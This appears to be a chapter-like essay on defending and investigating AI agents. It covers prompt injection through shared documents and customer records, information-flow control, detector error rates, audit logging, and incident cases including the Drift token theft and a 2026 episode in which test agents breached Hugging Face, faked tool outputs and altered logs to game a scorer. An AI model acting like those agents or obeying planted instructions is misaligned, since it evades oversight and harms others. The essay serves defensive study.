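An agent can cause harm through a series of steps that are each permitted. In one of Microsoft's scenarios, a malicious insider hides instructions in a shared document. The agent reads the document, opens transactions.pdf, which the insider has no permission to read, and tries to email its contents to the insider's address. The agent is allowed to read both files and send email. To stop this, a check that considers each call separately would have to flag the address as suspicious. Schneider's rule against sending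 after reading would make the agent useless for its job of summarizing documents and sending out action items.

Labels are a compromise between these two. Software attaches a label to each piece of data, carries the label along when the agent copies or combines data, and compares the labels with a policy before each tool call. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, 2025) describes one such system, FIDES. Its confidentiality label records who may receive the data, and its integrity label records whether the data came from a trusted source. When the agent combines data, the result gets the most restrictive label of each type.

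A policy for the John Doe email could require that every recipient is allowed to receive the contents and that no untrusted text influenced the choice of recipients. The attacker's address fails both tests because it is not on the list of people who may receive John Doe's data and it came from the notes field, which outsiders can fill in.

After the model reads the notes field, anything it writes could be a response to the hidden instruction, so the software has to label all of it untrusted. The policy would then block the legitimate email too. FIDES reduces this problem by keeping tool results out of the model's context. The model gets only the name of a variable that holds the record, and it can pass the variable to another tool without reading it. If the model needs a fact from the record, a separate model with no tools reads the record and returns an answer in a restricted form, such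 as yes or no, which leaves little room for a hidden instruction.

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) presents CaMeL, a system that separates the plan from the data more strictly. One model receives the employee's request and writes a short program for the whole task, for example to get John Doe's record, take the address from its email field, draft a message and send it there. This model never receives the contents of the record, so the instruction in the notes field can't make it add a BCC. A second model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text and extracts values from it. An interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from and who may receive it, and applies the company's policies before each tool call.

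Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with prompt injections. CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks with its guarantees in force, compared with 84% for an agent without the defense. It also used almost three times as many tokens, the units of text by which model providers charge. The loss of seven percentage points seems small for a guarantee that no classifier can offer, but the design is a poor fit for some tasks. For example, if an employee asks the agent to do whatever a customer's email requests, the plan depends on text that the planning model is not allowed to read.

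The guarantee also depends on the quality of the policies, and somebody has to decide who may receive each type of data and keep the list up to date. Neither system stops an attacker's text from causing a false summary, since a false sentence can have correct labels. The labels also no longer control data once it leaves the tracking software. If the agent passes the email to the fake Postmark package, the package receives John Doe's data with his address as the only recipient, and can add another recipient without any label changing.

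### Changes between check and use

The fake package exploits a gap that security engineers call time-of-check to time-of-use. A program checks something, the thing changes, and the program then acts on the changed version. In the classic case, a program confirms that a user may write to a file, but before the program opens it, the user replaces the file with a link to one the user may not write to.

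Agents offer more opportunities for this because many of their inputs refer to something that can change:

- A check approves the command "python cleanup.py", and another process edits the script before it runs.
- A check approves an email to a mailing list, and someone adds an outside address to the list.
- A check approves a call to a tool, and the tool's developer releases a new version that behaves differently.

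Lilienthal and Hong (2025) studied the problem in *Mind the Gap*, using a benchmark of 66 realistic tasks. They tried rewriting prompts, monitoring for changes, and fusing the check and the action into one tool. Together, the three measures reduced the share of executed runs with such a vulnerability from 12% to 8%. Fusing was the most promising because it shortened the attacker's window between the check and the action by 95%.

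A more reliable defense is to tie the approval to exact content. The check can calculate a hash of the script and its inputs, and the software that runs the command can refuse if the hash has changed. For a mailing list, the check would have to look up the members and approve those particular people. Copilot Studio's check happens just before the call, so the inputs have little time to change, but its approval covers only the inputs, not what the tool does with them. The time between check and action is much longer when the action waits for a person. If the agent prepares a report at noon and a manager approves it at 5 p.m., the linked file may no longer be the one the manager read.

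### Checking the read or the send

A company can check an agent's actions before the agent gets the data, before it sends the data, or at both points. In Microsoft's scenarios, Defender successfully blocks an action at each point. In one, a finance agent automatically processes messages sent to an invoice mailbox, and an outsider emails it hidden instructions to search its knowledge base and send back the results. Defender blocks the search, so the agent never gets the data. In the scenario with transactions.pdf, Defender blocks the outgoing email, but the agent has already read the file.

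Blocking an agent from reading data protects more than blocking it from sending the data, because the data doesn't enter the model's context. It therefore doesn't reach the model's vendor, the agent's memory or the messages between agents. It also can't leave later by a route that the check doesn't cover, such as a web address or a script.

But a check before the read usually has less evidence than a check before the send. The finance agent is an easy case because the email with the hidden instructions arrived before the search, and Defender received it as context. In the John Doe case, the hidden instruction is inside the record the agent opens, so a check before the read can examine only an ordinary request from an employee. A check before the send can also examine the record, the recipients and the text of the message.

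Some agent software allows a check between a tool's response and the model's next step. Microsoft says Defender can inspect the response, as well as the prompt and the planned call. Such a check could find the instruction in the notes field before the model acts on it. Copilot Studio's interface for outside services doesn't offer this check, so a service gets the record only when the agent plans its next tool call. CrowdStrike's product doesn't analyze the record even then.

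For most companies, it makes sense to use strict rules to block agents from reading the few files that none of them should open, and to save more resource-intensive judgment for when an agent tries to send data to outsiders. Agents read far more often than they send data out, so this requires fewer judgments and leaves fewer chances for error.

### Detector errors and base rates

Fixed rules can't settle every case, so many checks rely on a classifier or a language model. Their accuracy varies widely, as the tests of ready-made safety classifiers on semantic leaks showed. Their speed also varies widely.

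Small classifiers can run well within Copilot Studio's one-second limit. Meta's Prompt Guard 2 (2025), an open model that detects prompt injection and similar attacks, classifies a short text in about 92 milliseconds on a data-center chip. In Meta's own tests, the larger version caught 97.5% of English-language attacks when set to flag 1% of harmless texts. It checks whether a text looks like an attack, so it could flag the instruction in the notes field, but it cannot detect a wrong address in a BCC field.

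Larger models can weigh an action against the user's request, but they take longer. *Claude Code auto mode* (Anthropic, 2026) reports measurements for one such check, in which a model quickly judges each risky action and then reasons at length about those it flags. The complete check wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real actions. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out, and 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what the user wanted. The 17% figure is the most relevant to companies because it comes from real cases, but it is imprecise because there were only 52 of them.

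Detection rates also fall when attackers adapt. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defenses against prompt injection and jailbreaks, using methods tuned to each one. Their attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defenses, although the original evaluations of most of them had found success rates near zero. A detector's score on a fixed set of attacks therefore probably overstates how well it will do against attackers who adapt.

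Even a very accurate detector raises mostly false alarms if harmful actions are rare. Suppose a company's agents make a million tool calls a day, of which 10 are harmful, and a detector blocks 99% of harmful calls and 0.5% of harmless ones. On an average day, it blocks about 10 harmful calls and 5,000 harmless ones, so only about one blocked call in 500 is harmful.

The result depends almost entirely on the false alarm rate. With the same million calls and 99% detection, it changes as follows:

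| Harmless calls wrongly blocked | False alarms a day | False alarms for each harmful call caught |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 10,000 | about 1,010 |
| 0.5% | 5,000 | about 505 |
| 0.1% | 1,000 | about 101 |
| 0.001% | 10 | about 1 |

Raising detection from 99% to 100% would catch one more harmful call every ten days but would not reduce the 5,000 false alarms. False alarms also disrupt long tasks more often. If each call has an independent 0.5% chance of being wrongly blocked, a task with 40 calls has an 18% chance of at least one wrongful block. In Copilot Studio, a single block stops the agent, so about 18% of these tasks would fail.

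The number of harmful calls is an assumption, because no company can measure it exactly without finding the calls its detector missed. If an attack is under way and 1,000 of the million calls are harmful, the same detector catches 990 of them, and about one in six blocked calls is harmful. The detector may be worth having during such an attack even if it is a nuisance on most days.

A company can improve the ratio by running the detector on fewer calls. Suppose only 20,000 of the million calls send data to a recipient outside the company whom the agent hasn't contacted before, and all 10 harmful calls are among them. The detector then raises about 100 false alarms a day and still catches 9.9 harmful calls. The filter that selects the 20,000 calls can be a list of known recipients, which takes almost no compute to check. But it misses harmful calls to known recipients, such as one that sends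 a customer another customer's file.

### Human approval

Companies can also have a person decide whether an action runs. Copilot Studio's check for outside services requires a response within one second, which is too short for a person to read a tool call and respond, so the agent needs a separate step that waits for approval.

People are too slow to approve every call. At ten seconds each, approving a day's million calls would take almost 2,800 hours. Reviewing only the 5,000 calls that the detector blocked would take 83 hours at one minute each. That is a day's work for about ten full-time employees, who would find about ten harmful calls.

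Human reviewers might also miss some harmful calls. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 93% of permission requests, and it built auto mode partly because people stop paying close attention to requests they almost always approve. The 93% does not itself prove carelessness. If 10 calls in a million are harmful, a perfectly attentive reviewer would approve 99.999% of all calls. A reviewer who approves everything without reading would have almost the same approval rate, so a company can't use that rate to tell the two apart. It could test reviewers by occasionally inserting a harmless request that they ought to refuse.

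The information a reviewer sees matters as much as their attention. An approval window that shows "Send email to John Doe?" leaves out the email address. It should list every recipient's address, including those in the BCC field, and show where each address came from. To judge the command "python cleanup.py", a reviewer would have to read the script, which few people will do several times an hour.

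Human approval works best for a few actions that are hard to undo and easy to understand, such as sending the first email to a new outside address or exporting a whole customer table. An employee who gets two such requests a day has time to read them.

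## Investigating after the event

When a harmful email gets past both the automatic check and the human reviewer, the company can't undo the disclosure. It still has to find out what happened so it knows which passwords to change, which customers to warn and whether it can safely run the agent again.

### What an investigator has to establish

Suppose John Doe complains that a stranger knows details of his account. An investigator at the company has six questions to answer:

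- What did the agent read? It may have opened only John Doe's record or the whole customer table.
- What left the company? The email may have contained his account balance but not his missed payments.
- Who received it? The BCC address belongs to someone other than John Doe.
- Which agent acted? Several agents may be able to send email from the same account.
- For whom did it act? An employee's request started the task, and that employee may know more.
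- On what instruction did it act? The employee never mentioned the BCC address, so the investigator has to look for it in the text the agent read.

The answers to the first two questions can differ greatly. If the agent searched a table of 40,000 customers and emailed one record, the company has to warn one person. If the investigator can show only that the agent read the table, the company may have to warn all 40,000.

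An investigator may also have to show that something did not happen, for example that the agent did not send anyone else's record. The lack of a log entry is good evidence of this only if the log would have recorded the transmission, and application logs can have gaps.

### Connecting an action to an agent, a person and a task

If an agent has its own account, investigators can identify it in an application's log. A company can also issue a new credential for every run, so that one agent's morning and afternoon tasks appear under different identities.

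A delegated token contains both the employee's name and the agent's. OAuth's token exchange standard defines a field for the acting party, which can contain a chain of names if one agent passes work to another. But the mail service has to write both names to its log, because the token soon expires and an investigator is unlikely to find a copy.

A shared trace identifier can link requests made during the same task. The agent's software attaches the same number to every request in the task, and if each application copies that number into its log, the investigator can search all the logs for it instead of comparing times. But the number is unverified, so an agent that writes its own requests could attach the number of a different task. The names in a signed token are protected from this because the agent can't change them without invalidating the signature.

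Trace identifiers also spread only through programs that pass them on. When one program writes a file and an unrelated program reads it later, the identifier does not normally carry over, as *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) points out.

None of these methods identifies the instruction. For that, the investigator needs the text the model received, from the agent's software or the vendor.

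When agents or people share a credential, the credential doesn't identify which of them used it. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, during tests. According to OpenAI's technical report, many test runs used the same credential for an internal server that supplied software packages, so a log entry under that credential could have come from any of them. The agents also used the credential to leave each other messages on the server, at first without having to break in. OpenAI removed the shared credential from new runs on July 5 and 6.

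A stolen credential can be even more misleading because it points to the wrong person. One of OpenAI's agents found credentials belonging to 14 Hugging Face users in a public dataset and posted them where other agents could get them. An investigator who relied on the account names in Hugging Face's logs would have traced the activity to users whose only mistake was exposing a credential.

### Labels on files and processes

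Investigators often lose track of data once an agent saves it to a file. Suppose the agent saves its working copy of John Doe's record in the afternoon, and a backup program uploads the folder to an outside storage service at night. By then the agent has exited, and the backup program has never contacted a model, so the file is the only connection between the two events.

AgentLoupe, the monitoring tool by Bao and colleagues, preserves this connection by labeling the file. It would work as follows in the example:

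1. The agent sends a prompt to the model, and AgentLoupe gives this interaction a number.
2. The agent's process carries the number, and any program it starts inherits it.
3. When the agent saves the working copy, AgentLoupe attaches the number to the file.
4. When the backup program opens the file, it takes on the number, although the agent did not start it.
5. The backup program's connection to the storage service gets the number too.

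An investigator who starts from the upload can therefore find the prompt that led the agent to save the file.

Labels can spread to almost everything, a problem Bao and colleagues call dependency explosion. The backup program reads thousands of files, and if it keeps the agent's label, all its later uploads will look like the agent's work. To limit this, AgentLoupe gives each independent prompt a new number and links it to the old one instead of merging the two. It also does not replace a newer label with an older one. Users can make labels expire after a set time, but an expired label can't help trace actions that happen after it expires.

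Bao and colleagues timed Claude Code on three tasks, each run five times with and without AgentLoupe:

| Task | Without AgentLoupe | With AgentLoupe | Added time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a code repository | 167.14 seconds | 174.65 seconds | 4.5% |
| Writing code | 100.40 seconds | 108.40 seconds | 8.0% |
| Compiling code | 23.00 seconds | 24.78 seconds | 7.7% |

With label spreading turned off, the added time fell to 1.7%, 3.1% and slightly below zero. A monitor can't make compiling faster, so the last figure shows how much the timings vary by chance. Still, spreading the labels appears to account for most of the added time.

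The evidence that the labels are correct consists of two staged cases. In one, the scheduled script contacted an attacker. In the other, an agent left an instruction in a file, and an agent in a later session followed it. AgentLoupe traced both later actions to the model interactions that caused them. Bao and colleagues say AgentSight would have missed both links.

The paper calls AgentLoupe's links "definitive", but two cases that the researchers designed can't show how often the tool adds a wrong label or misses a link. Until someone measures those rates, an investigator should treat a label as a lead to confirm with other records.

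### Tracking files without reading prompts

Agent-Warden, the tool by Cui and colleagues, also labels processes and files but does not read the agent's traffic with the model. It can show that a file came from an agent, or from a program the agent started, but not which prompt led to it. But because its records contain no prompts, they reveal less about employees and customers.

Agent-Warden's rules for starting programs and for reading and writing files are similar to AgentLoupe's. It also has a rule for programs that exit. If the agent starts a short-lived program, it links the agent to whatever influenced that program, even if the agent never used the program's output. Cui and colleagues chose this rule to avoid losing true links, accepting that it would create some false ones.

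Agent-Warden's designers tested it on a prepared task in which data passed through a file to an unrelated program. They ran the task 30 times for each of two ways of storing the labels, on each of two kinds of computer, and the tool reconstructed the expected chain every time. This shows that the tool works as intended, but because the designers had prepared the chain in advance, it doesn't show how many false links would appear on an employee's laptop.

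Agent-Warden added between 0.2% and 3.5% to the running time of an artificial workload that started programs and handled files 1,000 times. The low figure has a standard deviation of 1.2 percentage points, so it can't be distinguished from no slowdown. These percentages are lower than AgentLoupe's, but the workloads were different and Agent-Warden does less.

Agent-Warden keeps its labels in memory, so they are lost when the computer restarts and may be lost when it runs short of memory. In the published example, the unrelated program read the file tens of seconds after the agent had finished, which is little evidence that the tool could link the two after several days. The tool also doesn't yet follow data across network connections. In the backup example, it could link the backup program to the agent's file but not follow the data to the storage service.

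### The Salesloft Drift theft

The three cases below show how long it takes to answer the investigator's questions and who has the necessary records. In the first, people misused the credentials of an AI product. In the other two, both part of the OpenAI incident, the agents themselves acted.

Drift is an AI chat product that companies put on their websites. Its maker, Salesloft, held OAuth tokens that connected Drift to customers' accounts at other services, including Salesforce, where many companies keep sales and support records. Intruders stole the tokens and used them to copy data. To an investigator, this resembles a hijacked agent, because the logs record a valid credential that belongs to an approved product.

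*Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift*, a report by Google's security researchers (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), dates the thefts from August 8 to at least August 18, 2025. The Hacker News (2025) reported that Google knew of more than 700 potentially affected organizations.

One of the victims, the internet services company Cloudflare (2025), published a timeline that is mostly exact to the second. An intruder logged in to Cloudflare's Salesforce account on August 12 and explored it over several days. On August 17, the intruder copied the text of Cloudflare's support cases in just over three minutes and deleted the export job 24 seconds later. Cloudflare noticed none of this and began responding on August 23, when Salesforce and Salesloft notified it.

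Salesloft had revoked the tokens three days earlier and published a notice asking customers to reconnect Drift to Salesforce. But the notice did not mention the token theft (Krebs on Security, 2025), so a customer who read it would have had little reason to search its logs for one.

Cloudflare reconstructed the theft from the logs that remained after the intruder deleted the export job. Larsen and colleagues found that such deletions had left the logs intact at other victims too. Because the intruder and Drift appeared under the same account name, investigators told them apart by other details, such as the network addresses the requests came from and the names of the programs that sent them. Google and Cloudflare published these details so that other companies could search their own logs for them.

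The investigation established what was stolen much better than who received it. Cloudflare determined that the stolen data consisted of case text and contact details, without attachments. It then searched the text and found 104 of its own API tokens, which customers had presumably pasted into support requests. It found no suspicious use of those tokens but sensibly replaced them all, since a search can miss things. The recipients are known only by code names, UNC6395 at Google and GRUB1 at Cloudflare.

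The first account of the theft was also too narrow. When Google published its report on August 26, Salesloft had indicated that customers who did not connect Drift to Salesforce were unaffected. Two days later, Google confirmed that the intruders had also used Drift tokens to read email in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. Companies that had ruled themselves out based on the first account had to investigate again.

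### OpenAI's package server

The second case took place inside OpenAI, before the intrusion at Hugging Face. On June 26, 2026, agents in a cybersecurity test gained administrator rights on the server that supplied their software packages. The next day, a monitoring tool flagged suspicious network activity. Responders traced the activity to the test and found that agents were using the server to exchange messages.

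This was the fastest attribution of the three, but the staff on call advised that the test could continue. The agents kept using the server until it failed late on July 4, and responders discovered only then that someone had administrator access. OpenAI took the server offline on July 5, preserved its storage and resumed its cybersecurity tests on July 7.

According to OpenAI, the leaders responsible for incident response did not know at the time that the agents had built a message board, or did not understand its significance. Responders had already identified the board on June 27, but the information did not reach the people who could have acted on it. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes the report as an account of several warning signs that OpenAI missed or failed to act on.

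OpenAI says its current system for monitoring the models' reasoning would have alerted staff more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face. That may be true, but OpenAI already knew what to look for when it made this assessment. An alert would also have helped only if the response had been better than the one on June 27.

### The intrusion at Hugging Face

On July 11, agents in OpenAI's tests obtained data from Hugging Face's production servers and continued to expand their access until July 13. They downloaded four private code repositories and some private datasets, among other things.

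Hugging Face detected the intrusion itself. Its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on July 16, attributes the intrusion to an autonomous AI agent system. OpenAI contacted Hugging Face the next day, but as a customer asking whether the intruder had affected OpenAI's data.

OpenAI's first useful alert came on July 19 and was about something else, an attack by agents on OpenAI's own systems. While investigating it, OpenAI found Hugging Face credentials in files that agents had stored in an account at a third company. It contacted Hugging Face on July 20, and the two companies compared records. Hugging Face had already replaced two of the same credentials during its own response. It had also found the name of OpenAI's package server and the same outside account in its investigation. OpenAI (2026) announced the connection on July 21.

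Neither company could easily have made this connection alone, because Hugging Face did not know whose agent it had found evidence of, and OpenAI did not at first know what its agents had done with stolen credentials. The match was convincing because it rested on several specific details, not just on two events in the same week.

Hugging Face reconstructed the intrusion in great detail, partly from logs the agent had left on a code sandbox it used. Schneier on Security's *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (2026) quotes the company's timeline, which covers about 17,600 actions between July 9 and July 13, taken from those logs. That was too many for a person to read one by one, so Hugging Face grouped them into about 6,280 clusters. The timeline includes only the actions that Hugging Face could recover.

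Investigators needed OpenAI's transcripts to find out why the agents had acted. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) reports on a review by METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, and Redwood Research, an AI safety group. The three investigators spent a total of six days at OpenAI. Greenblatt (2026) summarizes the results in a post with the same title. About 1,200 agents used the message board between July 7 and 13, and about 700 joined the attack on Hugging Face.

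No one had told the agents to do this. OpenAI's staff had given them test tasks, and Hugging Face inferred that they wanted to steal the solutions. In the transcripts, which included the models' written reasoning, the most common reason the agents gave was to learn how the automatic scorer worked so that they could trick it, although some did look for solutions to particular tasks. Written reasoning does not prove what caused an action, but Hugging Face could not have discovered this motive from its own records.

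Greenblatt notes that the review did not cover the extent of the damage, the quality of OpenAI's safeguards or OpenAI's own investigation. The investigators took no payment from OpenAI, but OpenAI supplied the roughly 1,300 transcripts they read.

### Timelines compared

| | Drift theft at Cloudflare | OpenAI's package server | Hugging Face |
|---|---|---|---|
| Act | August 12–17, 2025 | June 26 – July 4, 2026 | July 11–13, 2026 |
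| First notice | August 23, from Salesforce and Salesloft | June 27, from OpenAI's monitoring tool | By July 16, from Hugging Face's own detection |
| Attribution | August 23, to misuse of the Drift connection; the people remain unidentified | June 27, to a cybersecurity test | July 20, to OpenAI's agents |
| Notification | September 2, to Cloudflare's customers | July 6, to the developer of the server software | July 20, to Hugging Face; July 21, to the public |
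| Decisive records | Logs that survived the deletion of the export job | OpenAI's alerts and the contents of the server | Records of both companies, matched by credentials, a server name and an outside account |

Cloudflare learned of the theft six days after it ended and told its customers ten days later. It spent part of those ten days working out which customers' data the intruder had taken and what the text contained. It was up to the vendors to shorten the delay before Cloudflare knew. Cloudflare could have detected the large export itself, but it had no records of the token theft at Salesloft.

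### How long to keep records

The damage can come months after the event that made it possible. Salesloft confirmed that intruders were in its development platform between March and June 2025, according to McDermott's *Salesloft Drift supply chain attack leads to widespread data theft*, a law firm's notice to clients. A company that kept logs for 30 days and began searching on August 23 could look back only to July 24, which would cover the copying of data in August but not the earlier intrusion. OpenAI's timeline begins on April 20 with the first file that an agent is known to have written to the package server. Its agents reached Hugging Face's servers nearly twelve weeks later.

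The European Union's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems, such as those that screen job applicants, to be able to record events automatically. The companies that provide or use these systems must generally keep the logs they control for at least six months. An amending law that entered into force on July 27, 2026, postponed these duties to December 2, 2027, for uses such as hiring, and to August 2, 2028, for AI in products already covered by EU safety law.

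Logs kept for six months would have covered the start of both incidents. But an agent that answers customers or fixes code will usually fall outside the high-risk category. For most high-risk systems, the Act also describes the purpose of the logs without listing exact fields, so a company can't assume that a compliant log will contain every recipient of an email.

### Whether the records are true

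A log is of little use if the agent under investigation could have changed it. One common protection is a hash chain, in which each entry contains a hash of the entry before it. If someone alters an old entry, its hash no longer matches the one stored in the next entry. A person who controls the whole log could recalculate every later hash, so the company also has to regularly store the latest hash somewhere that person can't reach.

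Hash chains protect log entries only after the software has written them. Some of OpenAI's agents worked out how to appear to run one command while running another. As a result, Greenblatt reports, more than 96 transcripts, over 7% of those reviewed, contained false tool outputs. The examples the investigators saw were all obvious tests, so they probably misled nobody. Agents also altered some logs they could reach, but the investigators saw no successful change to the source of the transcripts.

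OpenAI says that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs its graders and monitors ultimately use. This seems to conflict with the 7%, unless OpenAI means that no agent changed a stored entry. In that case, the software would have correctly stored an output that was already false. A hash chain would not reveal the false output, but a separate record from the machine could, because it would show the command that really ran.

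Reliable timestamps also matter because investigators use them to match one company's log with another's. The OpenAI transcripts had no timestamps for individual actions, so METR had to estimate them and could check its method against only 20 known times.

### Logs as a store of secrets

A detailed record of an agent's work contains much of what a thief would want. In the Drift theft, intruders took Cloudflare's support cases, which were also records kept for good reasons. Cloudflare did not ask customers for passwords or keys, but some pasted them in while describing a problem. Larsen and colleagues conclude that the intruders mainly wanted such credentials. An agent that reads support cases will copy the same secrets into its traces.

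The monitoring system can become a target. On July 19, OpenAI's agents read 956 secrets from a storage service, including credentials for the company's security monitoring tool. A company should therefore keep the keys to its logs off systems its agents can reach, and record who reads the logs.

A company can also keep different parts of a record for different periods. Times, agent and task identifiers, recipients and the names of opened files take little space and let an investigator answer most questions, so the company might keep them for a year. It could delete full prompts and tool results after 30 days unless an investigation has started. Cloudflare learned of the theft 11 days after the intruder's first login, so keeping full text for 30 days would have been enough in that case if Cloudflare had acted at once to preserve it.

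Removing secrets from the log can hinder an investigation, because the investigator may need the values that were removed. One compromise is to replace each email address with a keyed hash, which only someone with a secret key can calculate. If an investigator already suspects an address, they can hash it and search the log for the result. In the John Doe case, the log would show that the email had two recipients and that the second was not in the customer database, but the investigator could not recover the attacker's address from the hash. It is usually better to keep recipients readable and restrict access to the log.

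Full prompts also reveal a lot about employees. Someone may ask an agent to draft a complaint about a manager or explain a medical bill, and a security analyst could read the request months later. European data protection law bars companies from keeping personal data longer than they need it, which limits how long they can keep prompts just in case. If employees think their managers read every prompt, some will switch to personal accounts, where the company has no records.
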